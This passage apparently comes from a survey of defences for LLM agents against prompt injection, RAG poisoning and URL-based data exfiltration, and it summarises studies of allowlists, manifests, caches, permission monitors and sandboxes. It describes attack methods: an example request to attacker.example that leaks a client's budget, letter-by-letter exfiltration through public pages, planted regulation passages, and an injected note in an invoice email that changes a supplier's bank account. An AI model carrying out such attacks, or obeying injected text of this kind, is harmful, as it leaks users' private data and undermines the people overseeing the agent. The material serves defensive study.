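Caches and lists of exact URLs avoid this problem because software builds them automatically from the public web. But nobody has checked whether the pages are trustworthy, so an attacker's public page can end up in either. Both mainly stop the agent from leaking private data in its page requests. A cache also gives some protection against hostile text, since an attacker can't change the stored copy after the crawler's visit or show the agent a special version of the page.

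OpenAI's programming agent Codex uses cached search results by default. OpenAI says this reduces exposure to prompt injection, but still tells developers to treat the results as untrusted. *Indexed Web Search* (Vaughan, 2026) reports that Codex gained an intermediate mode in June 2026 that lets it search the live web but open only addresses that OpenAI's server approves.

### How an approved source can carry an attack

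A domain list approves a whole site, but the site's owner may not have written all of its content. A manufacturer's website can include customer reviews, and a government site can publish comments from anyone on a public consultation. A shared company inbox has the same weakness, because strangers write most of the mail. In the Salesforce attack, the hostile instructions came from the company's own customer database, where the attacker had put them using a public form.

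A source can also become unsafe after someone approves it. A colleague can change a shared document the next day, or an attacker can take over a supplier's account. A hash detects a later edit, but it doesn't help if the attacker uses a stolen account to submit a new document and someone approves it.

Guo and Wei (2026), in *Hidden-in-Plain-Text*, measured what can happen when such text gets through. They built 6,200 pages styled like social websites and placed instructions in parts of the page that text-extraction software often keeps. For each question, a search program retrieved five passages by default and gave them to a language model that had been told not to follow any instructions in them. The table gives the percentage of questions for which the model followed an instruction anyway.

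| Where the instruction was | No protection | Cleaned page code | Normalized characters | All protections |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hidden page elements | 34.0 | 12.3 | 33.1 | 5.0 |
| Text positioned off the screen | 30.1 | 9.8 | 29.3 | 4.6 |
| Image descriptions | 27.8 | 11.1 | 27.0 | 4.8 |
| Labels for screen readers | 9.6 | 9.3 | 9.4 | 5.1 |
| Invisible characters | 23.2 | 23.0 | 7.8 | 4.2 |
| Average | 24.9 | 13.1 | 21.3 | 4.7 |

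Cleaning the page code removes hidden elements, and normalizing replaces or deletes unusual characters. Each works against some hiding places but does almost nothing against others. The last column shows the results when every sentence of the answer must also cite a retrieved passage. With cleaning and normalizing together, the share of questions the system could answer fell by only about two percentage points, and cleaning added only about 3% to the response time.

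Guo and Wei also tested 2,350 real pages from blogs, product documentation and forums, many of them the kind an ordinary domain allowlist would admit. Without protection, fixed attacks succeeded for 22.7% of questions and attacks adapted to the system succeeded for 28.9%. With all protections, the rates were 4.3% and 5.4%.

In 49% of the remaining failures, the instruction was in the visible body text. Cleaning can't remove such an instruction without also removing the content the user wants. The citation rule was the most effective protection against these failures and reduced them by 78%.

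This test used Llama 3, Mistral and Qwen2.5, which are much older and weaker than the best current models, so 24.9% is far too high an estimate for an agent running on one of those. Guo and Wei didn't test an allowlist either, though they recommend combining their protections with a cautious choice of sources. Their results are most useful as evidence about cleaning, which an operator should apply to approved sites as well.

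The operator can also approve only part of a site. On a manufacturer's website, the operator could approve the folder of technical data sheets but not the reviews. On a forum, the operator could approve only posts by the company's own staff, if the software can verify who wrote them. If many people edit a document, the operator could approve one reviewed version, identified by its hash.

### A direct test of a document manifest

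The most direct test of a manifest is Yingyan He's November 2026 master's thesis, *Poisoning Attacks and Collaborative Defense Framework for LightRAG-Based Construction Regulation Knowledge Bases*, which attacked and tried to defend a question-answering system for British building regulations. The attacks used false facts instead of hidden instructions, a method called poisoning. Both methods exploit the fact that the model treats whatever it retrieves as evidence. A manifest doesn't examine what a document says, so it should work about equally well against both kinds of attack, though the thesis tested only poisoning.

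The system ran on LightRAG, an open-source program that stores documents both as short passages and as a graph. A language model builds the graph by extracting the things the documents mention and the relations between them. When a user asks a question, LightRAG retrieves from the passages and the graph and gives the results to the model that writes the answer.

Yingyan He indexed two official volumes as 850 passages and wrote 150 questions about them. The attacker could add documents but not change the existing ones. An attack counted as successful only if the answer contained the attacker's value, left out the correct one and wasn't a refusal.

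#### How the attacks worked

In the simpler attack, each planted passage repeated the target question word for word, so that the search would find it, and then gave a wrong value in a paragraph written like a regulation. With five such passages per question, the attack succeeded on 33 of the 150 questions in at least two of three runs. The correct value was missing from about 60% of the answers, so the attack often spoiled an answer even when it didn't insert the attacker's value.

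Planting more passages made the attack more effective, probably because a larger share of the cited references then supported the wrong value, which made it more persuasive. Planted passages made up about 22% of the cited references when there was one and about 42% when there were five. The improvement didn't come from the passages being easier to find, since the answer cited a single planted passage every time.

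A second attack targeted the graph. The planted text made a false claim about where a rule applies, using something mentioned in several parts of the regulations. This succeeded on 22 questions. The thesis tested its defenses only against this weaker attack, on 72 poisoned questions and 78 others.

#### What the manifest did

The first defense gave each passage q a score that determined whether the model would see it. In simplified notation:

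score(q) = α × similarity + β × trust − γ × suspicion

Similarity measures how well the passage matches the question. Suspicion rises if the passage is nearly a duplicate of others or if only one search method found it. Trust is based on the manifest. A passage gets one point if its file is on the manifest and another if the hash matches, and it loses a point if the software can't trace it to the manifest. Every official passage therefore had a trust value of 2, and every planted passage had −1.

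Poison recall, the share of planted passages that the answer cites, fell from 0.969 without a defense to 0.000 with this defense. In one defended run, the search returned about 55 planted passages per poisoned question, but none of the 2,876 passages that reached the model came from a planted document. The attack success rate fell from 15.7% to 2.3%. The system refused none of the poisoned questions, and the share it answered correctly rose from 42% to 86%.

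The manifest pushed every unlisted document below the cutoff without checking whether it was false, so it would have excluded a true unlisted document too.

#### What the answer checker did

One of the two controls added in the full defense compared the graph's relations with a table of 145 official values and removed any that contradicted it. This had no measurable effect, partly because the attack disputed where a rule applied rather than the number in it.

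The other was an answer checker, a small model that tested whether each sentence of the answer followed from the evidence it cited. If not, the system withheld the answer and told the user to consult the original text.

The table covers all 150 questions, except that attack success counts only the 72 poisoned ones. A withheld answer counts as incorrect.

| Defense | Attack success | No answer given | Correct answers |
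|---|---|---|---|
| None | 15.7% | 2.4% | 65.8% |
| Manifest filter | 2.3% | 1.6% | 89.3% |
| Graph check | 16.7% | 2.0% | 66.9% |
| Answer checker | 4.6% | 76.0% | 12.4% |
| Manifest filter and answer checker | 0.0% | 71.3% | 26.2% |
| All three | 0.0% | 76.2% | 21.6% |

The full defense reduced attack success to zero but withheld answers to 76% of questions. Adding the answer checker to the manifest filter prevented the last 5 successful attacks in 216 attempts, but it also caused nearly all of the refusals. Because of the checker, the system stopped answering about seven in ten questions, most of which it would have answered correctly.

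In these runs, the checker withheld answers because it couldn't confirm them. It never found that the evidence contradicted an answer. LightRAG reports which file an answer came from but not which passage, so the checker had to compare each sentence with many unrelated passages. A checker given the right passage might do much better, so this result isn't evidence against checking answers in general.

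The manifest filter can also lower accuracy on a clean library, depending on which search methods the software compares to compute the suspicion score. Accuracy was unchanged in one version but fell by 32 percentage points in another, which compared a different search of the graph. The manifest can't have caused this drop, because it gives every official passage the same trust value. An operator could therefore keep the manifest and leave out the suspicion score.

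#### How text got around the manifest

The five attacks that still succeeded against the filter didn't cite any planted passage. When LightRAG indexes documents, it writes a short description of each item and relation in its graph. It merges text from several documents into one description without recording where each part came from. The filter checked passages but not these descriptions. For two poisoned questions, Yingyan He recorded everything the model received, three times each. The false claim was in the descriptions all six times and never in the passages.

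A test in the thesis with a real document showed the same gap. It used 20 questions that depended on a 2026 amendment. The system answered 3 correctly when the amendment was missing from the library, 17 when it was in the library but not on the manifest, and 16 after it was registered.

This result understates the effect of leaving a document off the manifest, because the amendment's wording still reached the model through the graph descriptions for 14 of the 16 questions where this could be measured. If the operator closed that gap, the score for an unregistered amendment would presumably fall to about 3 of 20, which is a better estimate of performance under a strict manifest that nobody keeps up to date.

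The operator should check the manifest before the software indexes a document, so that no summary or description can contain unapproved text. The thesis also recommends treating permission to add documents as a privileged role that requires a login and a record of every addition.

The person in that role needs a way to verify new documents. In another experiment, Yingyan He planted three forged notices of 2026 amendments. All 18 answers repeated the forged value and said it had replaced the original. A busy librarian could also trust a forged notice, so the office should download amendments directly from the government's site instead of accepting emailed copies.

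These results come from nearly ideal conditions for a manifest. The library contained two official volumes from a single publisher, and the attacker had no way to get a document approved. A company with thousands of documents written by hundreds of employees would have to decide whose documents to register, and the thesis doesn't show how well a manifest would work there. It also tested only one system and one DeepSeek model.

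### What the attack success rate hides

The full defense in the thesis would be almost useless in practice, even though its attack success rate of 0% is lower than the manifest filter's 2.3%. In *Prevented is Not Protected*, Dahal and Xiong (2026) found other ways that attack success rates can be misleading.

For each question, they compared four answers: with and without poisoned passages, and with and without a defense. This reveals attacks that a defense prevents as well as wrong answers that it introduces. Let P be the share of questions where the defense removes the attacker's answer, and J the share where the attacker's answer appears only after the defense is switched on. The net benefit is:

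N = P − J

One of the defenses tested was an adapted version of TrustRAG, which filters out suspicious passages and then has the model compare the rest with its own knowledge. On 100 HotpotQA questions, each with one planted passage, the model gave the attacker's answer 60 times without the defense. TrustRAG removed that answer in 20 cases but introduced it in 20 others, so there was no net reduction. Counting only the prevented attacks would make it look as if TrustRAG had stopped a third of the attacks that succeeded without it.

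But those counts came from a program that searched each answer for the attacker's words. When Dahal and Xiong read the 40 changed answers, they confirmed 16 of the 20 preventions but only 6 of the 20 introductions. In the other 14 introductions, the model mentioned the attacker's answer while questioning or rejecting it. A separate check, using a language model as the judge, classified 35 answers as endorsing the attacker's claim without TrustRAG and 11 with it.

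The scoring method can reverse a ranking. On a second dataset, Natural Questions, the word search found 42 attacker answers for a competing defense and 46 for TrustRAG, which made the competitor look slightly better. But the judging model counted 20 endorsements of the attacker's answers for the competitor and only 7 for TrustRAG.

It is still unclear how useful TrustRAG's answers are. On 200 ordinary HotpotQA questions without poison, the judging model couldn't decide whether 147 of the answers were correct. An answer can avoid endorsing the attacker but still be too vague to help the user.

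Dahal and Xiong also tested detectors that look for unusual patterns in the search scores. When one of the five retrieved passages was planted, two of these detectors caught 59 of 60 successful attacks on HotpotQA. With five planted passages per question, they caught none of 96. A single planted passage stands out from the rest, but when most of the retrieved passages are planted, there are few clean ones to compare them with.

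A manifest doesn't have this weakness because it checks each document separately, however many are planted. In the LightRAG thesis, the filter kept out all five planted passages for each question. For a library with known publishers, checking a document's source therefore seems more dependable than trying to recognize poisoned text.

Telling the model to be careful with unreliable evidence raised its endorsements of the attacker's claim on HotpotQA to 61 out of 100, from 35 without the warning. Dahal and Xiong tested Llama 3 8B, a small, old model, and a current one may well handle the warning better.

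Defenses for systems that retrieve documents are often poorly tested. *Protection Is Not One Event* (Liu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 118 papers on protecting these systems. Most used general question sets and attackers who didn't adapt, and the papers measured such different events that their success rates often can't be compared. An operator testing an allowlist should at least count withheld answers and correct answers as well as successful attacks.

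### Fetching a page also sends data

On the web, a retrieval allowlist also has to prevent leaks, because an agent fetches a page by sending its address to the site's server. The address can contain more than a location. Suppose a hostile page tells the architect's agent to open this address:

```
attacker.example/log?client=Harper&budget=2400000
```

The server's owner can read the client's name and budget in the log of requested addresses, even if the server returns nothing useful. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that this can happen in the background, for example when the agent loads an image, so the user may never notice.

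Approval prompts don't help much. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* notes that users usually approve a search tool as a whole and don't see each address it requests. Even detailed logs often shorten long addresses, and an attacker can encode the data to look like an ordinary tracking code.

A strict allowlist of destinations stops this kind of leak. In tests reported in *The Framing Gap* (2026), one blocked every attack, however the attacker encoded the data, but it also blocked legitimate requests to sites not on the list.

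#### Why OpenAI rejected a list of trusted sites

OpenAI considered letting ChatGPT open links only to well-known sites, but gives two reasons for not relying on this. First, many trusted sites have redirects, which forward visitors to another address. If the software checks only the first address, an attacker can use a redirect to send the agent to a hostile site. Second, a strict list would produce frequent warnings about harmless sites, and users would get used to clicking through the warnings.

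The first problem can be solved by checking the address again after every redirect. The second is harder to solve for a general assistant, whose users visit millions of different sites. The architect's office needs perhaps thirty sites, so a list would cause far fewer warnings there.

#### The index of exact URLs

OpenAI instead checks whether the exact address was already public. Its crawler explores the web as a search engine does, without access to anyone's conversations or accounts, and records the addresses it finds in an index. When ChatGPT is about to open an address automatically, the software looks for it in this index. If the address is there, the page loads. Otherwise, the software tells the agent to try another site or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation.

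The reasoning is that an address the crawler found independently is unlikely to contain this user's secrets. The address with Harper's budget would fail the check because it didn't exist before the attack. OpenAI says the index protects only against leaks through the address. A page can pass the check and still contain false information or hostile instructions.

An agent can still leak some data through its choice of pages. The security blog Embrace The Red describes the method in *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. An attacker publishes 36 ordinary pages, one for each letter and digit, and waits for the crawler to index them. The attacker then uses a hidden instruction to get the agent to spell out a name by opening the matching pages in order. The sequence of requests reveals the name, even though every address is public.

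Choosing one of n pages reveals log₂(n) bits of information, so each request reveals about 5.2 bits (one character) with 36 pages and 12 bits (slightly more than two characters) with 4,096. This is far too slow for stealing a large file but fast enough for a password or a client's name. Embrace The Red suggests preventing the agent from requesting the same page twice in a session, which would make it harder to spell a word with repeated letters.

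Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* restricts the model to addresses that the user has provided or that earlier searches and fetches have returned, rather than to an index of the whole web. The model therefore can't build a new address out of private data. In 2026, Ayush Paul used a similar attack to get around the corresponding rule in Claude's chat service, which also allowed links on pages that Claude had already opened (Willison, 2026).

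Paul built a site where he claimed that AI assistants had to identify their user by spelling out the details one letter at a time. Each page had links for choosing the next letter. The site displayed this text only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking the page would have seen nothing wrong. Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic then stopped Claude's web-fetching tool from following links on pages it had fetched.

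Many applications paste emails or documents into the message they send to the model, and the tool then treats any web address in that text as if the user had supplied it (Willison, 2025). It also does this with addresses in results from tools that the developer's application runs. Anthropic now offers a setting that rejects addresses found only in those results, and an operator whose agent reads outside email should use it.

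### Lockdown Mode and cached pages

If the agent reads only stored copies, the attacker's server receives no requests, so even spelling out a name letter by letter fails. Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting, is based mainly on this idea. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced it in February for business and institutional customers, and OpenAI began extending it to personal accounts in June.

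In ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode, web browsing uses only cached pages, and no live browsing request leaves OpenAI's network. ChatGPT also can't download files, retrieve images from the web or let code it writes connect to the network. Deep Research, which compiles long reports from many sources, and Agent Mode, which acts on websites for the user, are disabled. OpenAI turned off such features where it couldn't use fixed rules to guarantee that data would stay inside its network.

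These rules are ordinary software, so even a clever injection can't create an exception to them. Willison has praised Lockdown Mode for that reason, but he also concludes that ChatGPT without it lacks robust protection against a determined attacker. OpenAI considers the mode unnecessary for most users and recommends it for people such as executives and security staff. In its announcement, OpenAI bases its case for the mode on how it works and gives no measured attack success rates.

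OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* help page warns that even with the mode on, hostile instructions in a cached page or an uploaded file can reach the model and change its answer. If a cached page gives a false width for an escape stair, the architect may get the wrong width, even though no client data leaks.

Data can also leave through connected apps. In company workspaces, Lockdown Mode doesn't switch off every app, and administrators choose which actions to allow. OpenAI advises against allowing any action that writes data where an outsider might be able to see it. For instance, an agent that can comment on a public project page could post a secret there without opening a web address. Lockdown Mode also doesn't affect Codex's network access, and personal users can turn it off for a single chat.

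The main drawbacks are missing and outdated pages. OpenAI also offers cached browsing as a separate feature, and its *Offline web search in ChatGPT* warns that pages may be absent, incomplete or older than the live version. An old copy of building regulations, for example, may state a rule that no longer applies. If a page isn't in the cache, OpenAI's *Offline web search for ChatGPT workspaces* suggests that users provide the material themselves. However, the file they upload may contain the same hostile text as the live page, and no crawler or administrator has checked it.

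The architect's office can use different forms of allowlist for different tasks. For questions about regulations, it can limit the agent to documents on the manifest, because a wrong answer could make a building unsafe and there are few official sources. For comparing products, it can start a separate session that reads cached pages from many manufacturers but has no access to client files. An injected instruction could still distort the comparison, so the architect should check the chosen product's data sheet before ordering.

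## What simulation shows about permission limits

Some hostile text will get past almost any retrieval allowlist, and the damage then depends on what the agent is permitted to do. In November 2026, Aljumaily and colleagues published a simulation that runs the same attacks against agents with increasingly strict permission checks. Some of the simulated tools control industrial equipment, which would be dangerous to attack in a real test.

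The simulation has 13 tasks and 12 tools. Five tools only read data (web pages, files, emails, folder listings or a database). The other seven send email, post data to websites, write files, delete files, change configurations, run shell commands or adjust a setpoint, which is the target value a machine is set to maintain. A task normally takes one to three tool calls, and the attacker's instruction is in something the agent reads during the task.

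There are five types of attacker. Three make a single attempt each: one gives a plain instruction, one falsely claims authority and one disguises its instruction. The fourth is adaptive. It makes up to 25 attempts, tries three versions of the arguments each time and remembers which ones failed. The fifth and strongest tries every attack in the library in every version, and the model always obeys it.

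Each attack gets a harm score for the worst action the agent carried out, using the severity scale described earlier. Writing a file scores 3, sending an email 5, deleting a file 7, running a shell command or posting data to a website 8, changing a configuration or a setpoint 9, and sending out confidential data 10. A failed attack scores 0, and Aljumaily and colleagues call any score of 8 or higher severe.

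### Real code and assumptions

The simulation used real code for the tasks, the permission checks, the attacker's search for a version of the attack that gets through, and the scoring. The scoring program compared each action with what the user had authorized, without using the monitor's verdict. The tools were harmless stand-ins.

The model's obedience, the human reviewer and the tracking of untrusted text were assumptions. In simplified notation, the chance that the model obeys an injected instruction is:

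P(obey) = σ(a₀ + u + b × s − δ)

The function σ converts any number into a probability. The model's general tendency to obey is a₀, and u adjusts it for the task. The strength of the attack is s, with weight b, and δ is the protection provided by a defensive prompt or similar measure. With the default values and no task adjustment, an attack of strength 1 works 48% of the time without a defensive prompt and 17% with one. For the adaptive attacker, s grows and δ shrinks with each attempt, so every defence that relies on the model eventually fails.

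Aljumaily and colleagues tested how much the results depend on this formula by varying a₀ from −4 to 4. Across that range, the success rate of a single disguised attack rose from 2.2% to 98.2% against a defensive prompt, and from 0.5% to 7.7% against the strictest permission check. The simulation is therefore weak evidence of how well prompts work, but the permission check kept the success rate low even when the model was very likely to obey the attack.

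### Results against a fully compromised model

The obedience formula plays no part in the next results, because the model always obeys.

| Permission check | What it examines | Attacks that succeed | Severe attacks | Average harm |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | Nothing | 100% | 100% | 10.00 |
| Tool allowlist | The tool | 92% | 62% | 7.08 |
| Naive argument checks | The tool and its arguments, with simple comparisons | 92% | 62% | 7.08 |
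| Hardened argument checks | The same, with protection against disguised arguments | 62% | 8% | 2.92 |
| Task-bound permissions | Whether the user's request authorizes this exact call, and whether it would send out confidential data | 23% | 0% | 0.69 |

The table omits defensive prompts and injection detectors because they are useless when the model always obeys. Adding them to the task-bound permissions left harm at 0.69 and lowered completion of legitimate tasks by 4.5 percentage points.

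The attacker could get past the naive argument checks by disguising the arguments, for example by adding an address to a list of permitted recipients, or by putting a trusted site's name before an @ sign in a web address that leads elsewhere. Of 33 working versions of the attacks, the plain tool allowlist admitted 27, the naive checks 18, the hardened checks 6 and the task-bound permissions 1. The naive and hardened checks performed equally well against attackers who don't vary their arguments, so an operator who tests only with fixed attacks could mistake a weak check for a strong one.

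The attacks that still succeed against task-bound permissions misuse an action that the user requested. An agent asked for a report on pressure readings needs permission to write that report, and if compromised, it can report a dangerous pressure as normal. Aljumaily and colleagues also give the example of a permitted email that contains a phishing link. The successful attacks in this test all appear to have been false files, which score 3 each, rather than emails, which score 5, because three false files spread over 13 tasks give the average harm of 0.69.

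The 23.1% success rate is 3 of the 13 tasks, 61.5% is 8, and 92.3% is 12. Repeating the simulation doesn't make these figures more precise, because the same tasks fail each time. Aljumaily and colleagues wrote the tasks and didn't weight them by how often they occur, so the tasks aren't a random sample of an agent's real work. Even if they were, 3 of 13 would be compatible with a true rate anywhere from about 8% to 50%, so the order of the permission checks is more informative than the exact percentages.

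The result for task-bound permissions is also a best case. The monitor permitted exactly the actions that the scoring program counted as authorized, so almost the only thing it could get wrong was the content of those actions. The 0.69 is therefore the harm that remains with a perfect policy, which a real operator is unlikely to have.

The simulation is similarly uninformative about lost work. Agents completed 98% of legitimate tasks behind the task-bound monitor, but Aljumaily and colleagues had assumed that 5% of tasks include a legitimate action the policy didn't foresee, and that the agent recovers from half of the resulting denials. Those two assumptions alone imply a completion rate of about 98%. Benchmarks of real permission systems have shown much larger losses on open-ended tasks.

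### Missing rules

Aljumaily and colleagues simulated an incomplete policy by removing rules at random, then measured the harm from a fully compromised model. The last column shows the results with a human reviewer added.

| Share of rules present | Harm with the monitor alone | Harm with the monitor and a reviewer |
|---|---|---|
| 100% | 0.69 | 0.27 |
| 80% | 1.62 | 0.80 |
| 60% | 3.21 | 2.17 |
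| 40% | 5.32 | 4.43 |
| 20% | 7.60 | 6.80 |
| 0% | 10.00 | 10.00 |

With a fifth of the rules missing, the harm more than doubles. The reviewer helps at most levels but can't replace the missing rules.

This simulation allows any action that has no rule, so a missing rule might go unnoticed until an attacker exploits it. Progent would block the action, and the operator would soon hear about the missing rule because legitimate work would stop.

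### Human review and a cap on requests

Unlike fixed rules, a person can judge whether a report is false. The simulated reviewer sees every call with a severity of at least 8 that the monitor has let through. The threshold drops to 3 if the session is marked as having read untrusted text. This marking is called taint tracking, and the simulation assumes that the mark survives in 95% of attacks.

The chance that the reviewer catches a bad call is:

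h = 0.9 × max(0.3, 1 − 0.3L) × 0.93^k

L, the average number of reviews per legitimate task, represents reviewer fatigue. The exponent k counts the attacker's earlier attempts and the earlier review requests in the session. At 0.57 reviews per task, the reviewer catches about 75% of bad calls at first, but only 36% when k reaches ten. These values are guesses about human behavior, so the results mainly show how review might fail.

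Reviewing only severe calls made no difference, because the task-bound monitor had already blocked all of them. With taint tracking, review lowered harm from 0.69 to 0.26 and the attack success rate from 23.1% to 8.7%, but required 0.57 reviews per legitimate task. Harm ranged from 0.11 to 0.39 depending on the assumptions about fatigue and repeated requests. Review had no benefit when the reviewer saw only calls with a severity of 5 or more, because the remaining attacks all scored 3.

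If taint tracking fails completely, the harm returns to 0.69 because the monitor still works. The failure is worse behind the hardened argument checks, which let some severe actions through. To save the reviewer work, an operator with that monitor might raise the general review threshold from 8 to 10 and rely on taint tracking for the rest, without noticing that one safeguard now depends on the other. If the tracking then fails, severe actions occur in 7.7% of attacks, compared with 1.7% under the old threshold.

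Without a monitor, a fully compromised agent achieved a severe action in every attack simulated by Aljumaily and colleagues, because it could keep making requests until the reviewer mistakenly approved one. Even with the effects of fatigue and repetition removed, it succeeded in 92.6% of attacks. A reviewer who misses a tenth of bad requests has about a 93% chance of approving at least one out of 25.

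A fixed cap on approval requests limits this tactic. After the agent reaches the cap, ordinary software denies all further requests in that session.

| Requests allowed per session | Severe attacks, reviewer only | Harm, reviewer only | Harm, reviewer and task-bound monitor |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 17.3% | 2.25 | 0.04 |
| 2 | 37.4% | 4.40 | 0.22 |
| 4 | 73.2% | 7.59 | 0.24 |
| 8 | 97.8% | 9.80 | 0.24 |
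| No cap | 100% | 10.00 | 0.24 |

The difference between 0.24 here and 0.26 above is random variation between runs. With the task-bound monitor, only a cap of one request makes a clear difference, and it lowers the completion of legitimate tasks by about half a percentage point. With the reviewer alone, the same cap lowers completion by about four points and still leaves more harm than the monitor does by itself. An attacker might also use up the single request so that the software denies a legitimate one later. The simulation leaves out attacks that only disrupt the agent's work.

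### Runs with two real models

Aljumaily and colleagues ran two small open models, Qwen2.5-1.5B and Qwen2.5-7B, behind the task-bound monitor on the same 13 tasks. The monitor admitted 2 of 156 attacks (1.3%) with the 1.5B model and 12 of 156 (7.7%) with the 7B model. All 14 were the false pressure report. If the 156 attacks were split equally among the tasks, each task had 12, and the 7B model wrote the false report every time.

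This supports the simulation's main result, because the only attacks that passed were ones the monitor couldn't have evaluated. The success rate still depended on the model, because the monitor guarantees only a limit on which actions are possible, and a model that follows instructions more readily will carry out more of the harmful actions still allowed.

The monitor also raised the smaller model's completion rate for legitimate tasks from 50% to 71%, because it blocked the unauthorized actions that the model often took even without an attacker. The larger model completed 99% of legitimate tasks with or without the monitor.

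The real runs contradicted the simulation's assumption that defences inside the model wear down until every attack succeeds. In the simulation, an adaptive attacker always defeats spotlighting (marking untrusted text so that the model can recognize it) combined with a detector. In the real runs, the larger model with both defences carried out none of the 156 attacks. For the smaller model, Aljumaily and colleagues estimated a 38% attack success rate after ten attempts. A defensive prompt alone was almost completely ineffective, with estimated attack success rates of 91% and 85% after ten attempts.

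However, the real attacks used fixed texts that nobody had adjusted to fool the detector. The results undermine the assumed decline, but they don't show what a skilled adaptive attacker would achieve.

Results from a separate check on the smaller model contradict the idea that attacks lie on a single scale of strength. The model followed half of the instructions that claimed to come from the document's owner, but only 4% of those presented as an urgent system notice, which the simulation treats as stronger. Each figure comes from 24 trials. When Aljumaily and colleagues replaced the obedience formula with the measured rates, the attack success rate against task-bound permissions after ten attempts stayed at 7.7%, or one task.

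### Tests that include an operating-system sandbox

The Aljumaily simulation covers neither operating-system isolation nor retrieval allowlists. If the monitor permits a shell command, the simulation scores the call without accounting for anything a sandbox would have blocked. It also places the hostile text in something the agent reads, so it can't measure the benefit of keeping that text out.

*Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents* (Jing, 2026) shows the sandbox's contribution most clearly. In its test, a program checked proposed actions against fixed rules, and an operating-system sandbox then limited those that passed. Of 117 commands designed to get past the rules, for instance by writing a forbidden path in an unusual way, 30.8% succeeded without the sandbox and 7.7% with it. Jing counted every request for approval as granted.

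The 7.7% came from a simulated sandbox. Jing then tried 94 of the commands in the real one and got a usable result for 66, of which 5 (7.6%) had an effect. The nearly equal totals hide frequent differences between the two sandboxes in which commands get through. The simulation assumed that a sandbox which blocks writing in a location also blocks deletion there. The real sandbox restricted deletion only on the disk volume that held the workspace, and it silently deleted a test file on another volume.

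Jing also ran the commands with the real sandbox turned off. In 88 comparable pairs, 45 commands that the sandbox had refused ran without it, and none changed in the other direction. In the corrected simulation, the sandbox blocked 11.1% of legitimate tasks, largely because the rules allowed work in a temporary folder that the sandbox kept closed.

How much a sandbox helps depends on what runs inside it. In *Names Are Not Objects*, Commey (2026) ran 74 scripted attacks on a Mac, with the attacker fully controlling a programming agent.

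| Configuration | Successful attacks | Held for approval | Legitimate operations completed | Legitimate workflows completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No limits | 74 | 0 | 46 of 46 | 7 of 7 |
| Tool allowlist | 66 | 0 | 46 of 46 | 7 of 7 |
| Tool allowlist and sandboxed commands | 56 | 0 | 46 of 46 | 7 of 7 |
| Sandboxed agent and commands, with a broker | 2 | 14 | 43 of 46 | 4 of 7 |

Sandboxing only the commands stopped just ten more attacks. The agent still ran outside the sandbox, and the commands inside could read any file. In eight attacks, the agent planted a file that the developer's tools would later run or use as instructions. The strictest configuration also puts the agent in a sandbox and sends its requests through a broker, a separate program that checks which file or program each request will affect. The two attacks that this configuration didn't stop sent a secret to an approved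 destination, once in encoded form and once in two halves.

The strictest result depends on people making good decisions at the approval step. When Commey removed that step, 18 more attacks succeeded. Commey wrote the attacks and the defence, and found eight flaws in the defence. Seven were versions of the problem the defence was meant to solve, in which software approves a name that later refers to something else.

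Even a flawless sandbox can't detect the misuse of an action that the task requires. *Taming AI Agents with seL4* (Alhindi, 2026) tested permissions enforced by seL4, a very small operating-system kernel whose isolation is mathematically proven in certain configurations. The test used a configuration without that proof and ran on an emulated computer. Each agent could call only the functions its task needed. On AgentDojo's banking and chat tasks with GPT-4o mini, the attack success rate fell from 48% to 7%. The task completion rate without attacks fell from 68% to 58%, though that difference could be due to chance.

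Alhindi then replaced the model with a script that tried everything an attacker would need. The kernel stopped 181 of 248 attacks, and the other 67 (27%) used only functions that the user's task required. In the test with the real model, about half of the successful attacks misused the payment function, which the agent needed to pay a bill. The kernel checked whether the agent could make a payment but not who received it. As in the Aljumaily simulation, the permissions came from the benchmark's own solutions, so they were close to ideal.

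The 27% is close to the 23% in the Aljumaily simulation, but probably by coincidence, since both figures depend on which attacks were tested. *Beyond Instruction Override* (2026) tested attacks that mostly change an argument of a tool the task already needs, and checks on the choice of tool blocked none of them. An operator should therefore ask how many of an attacker's goals could be achieved with the agent's ordinary tools, rather than expect a quarter of attacks to succeed everywhere.

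Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Lingering Authority*, measured blast radius as a weighted count of the sensitive resources that a programming agent reached or changed. In 17 scenarios with tempting but forbidden files and actions, the average was 6.65 with full access, 4.09 with a coarse sandbox, 2.73 with a fixed allowlist and 0 with permissions derived from the task. The sandbox still allowed violations in 86% of runs, and the allowlist in 82%. Neither could distinguish a file that the task needed from an equally accessible one that it didn't.

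The result of zero violations partly reflects the test's design, because the same written rules controlled the agent and defined a violation. In a separate set of programming tasks, completed runs fell from 180 to 161 out of 185 with the task-derived permissions. These permissions expire when the part of the task that needed them ends. Santos-Grueiro's system refused all ten attempts to reuse a permission after that point, while an otherwise identical system without expiry allowed all ten.

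Other simulations address different parts of the problem. Zhan, Forough and colleagues (2026), in *Airlock*, study how to contain bad data when other agents have already read it before an alert. After a late alert in their smart-home test, 13 bad commands got through when the system blocked only the source of the data, and none got through when it stopped everything that had used the data. *Reward Hacking and Agent Containment Failure* (2026) calculates the risk of an incident by multiplying the probabilities of five events, including an escape from containment. It assumes the strength of the isolation, so its results can't show how well isolation works.

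### Simulated limits on retrieval

Few tests measure how much a retrieval limit reduces successful attacks. *SearchInject* (2026) tested a filter on search results, which reduced the cases in which a planted instruction reached the model from 104 to 21. But the test found no confirmed hijacking even without the filter, so it can't show whether fewer attacks would succeed. The filter also worked by removing suspicious results, not by limiting retrieval to a list of approved sources.

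Standard benchmarks are poorly suited to testing an allowlist. Chen, Toyoda and colleagues (2026) point out in *IPI-proxy* that many use specially built hostile pages, which an agent restricted to approved sites can't open. An allowlist would get a perfect score on such a benchmark, but the more realistic danger of hostile text on an approved site would remain untested. Their software inserts attacks into pages from approved sites as the agent loads them.

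Alhindi tested a stricter limit on what agents read, in a simulated accounts department with five agents. The attacker's email came from a supplier's usual address and contained a genuine invoice. A note in it told AI assistants to change the supplier's bank account. The agent that read the email passed the note on, and it reached the coordinating agent in 23 of 40 runs. The coordinator changed the account in 7 of those runs.

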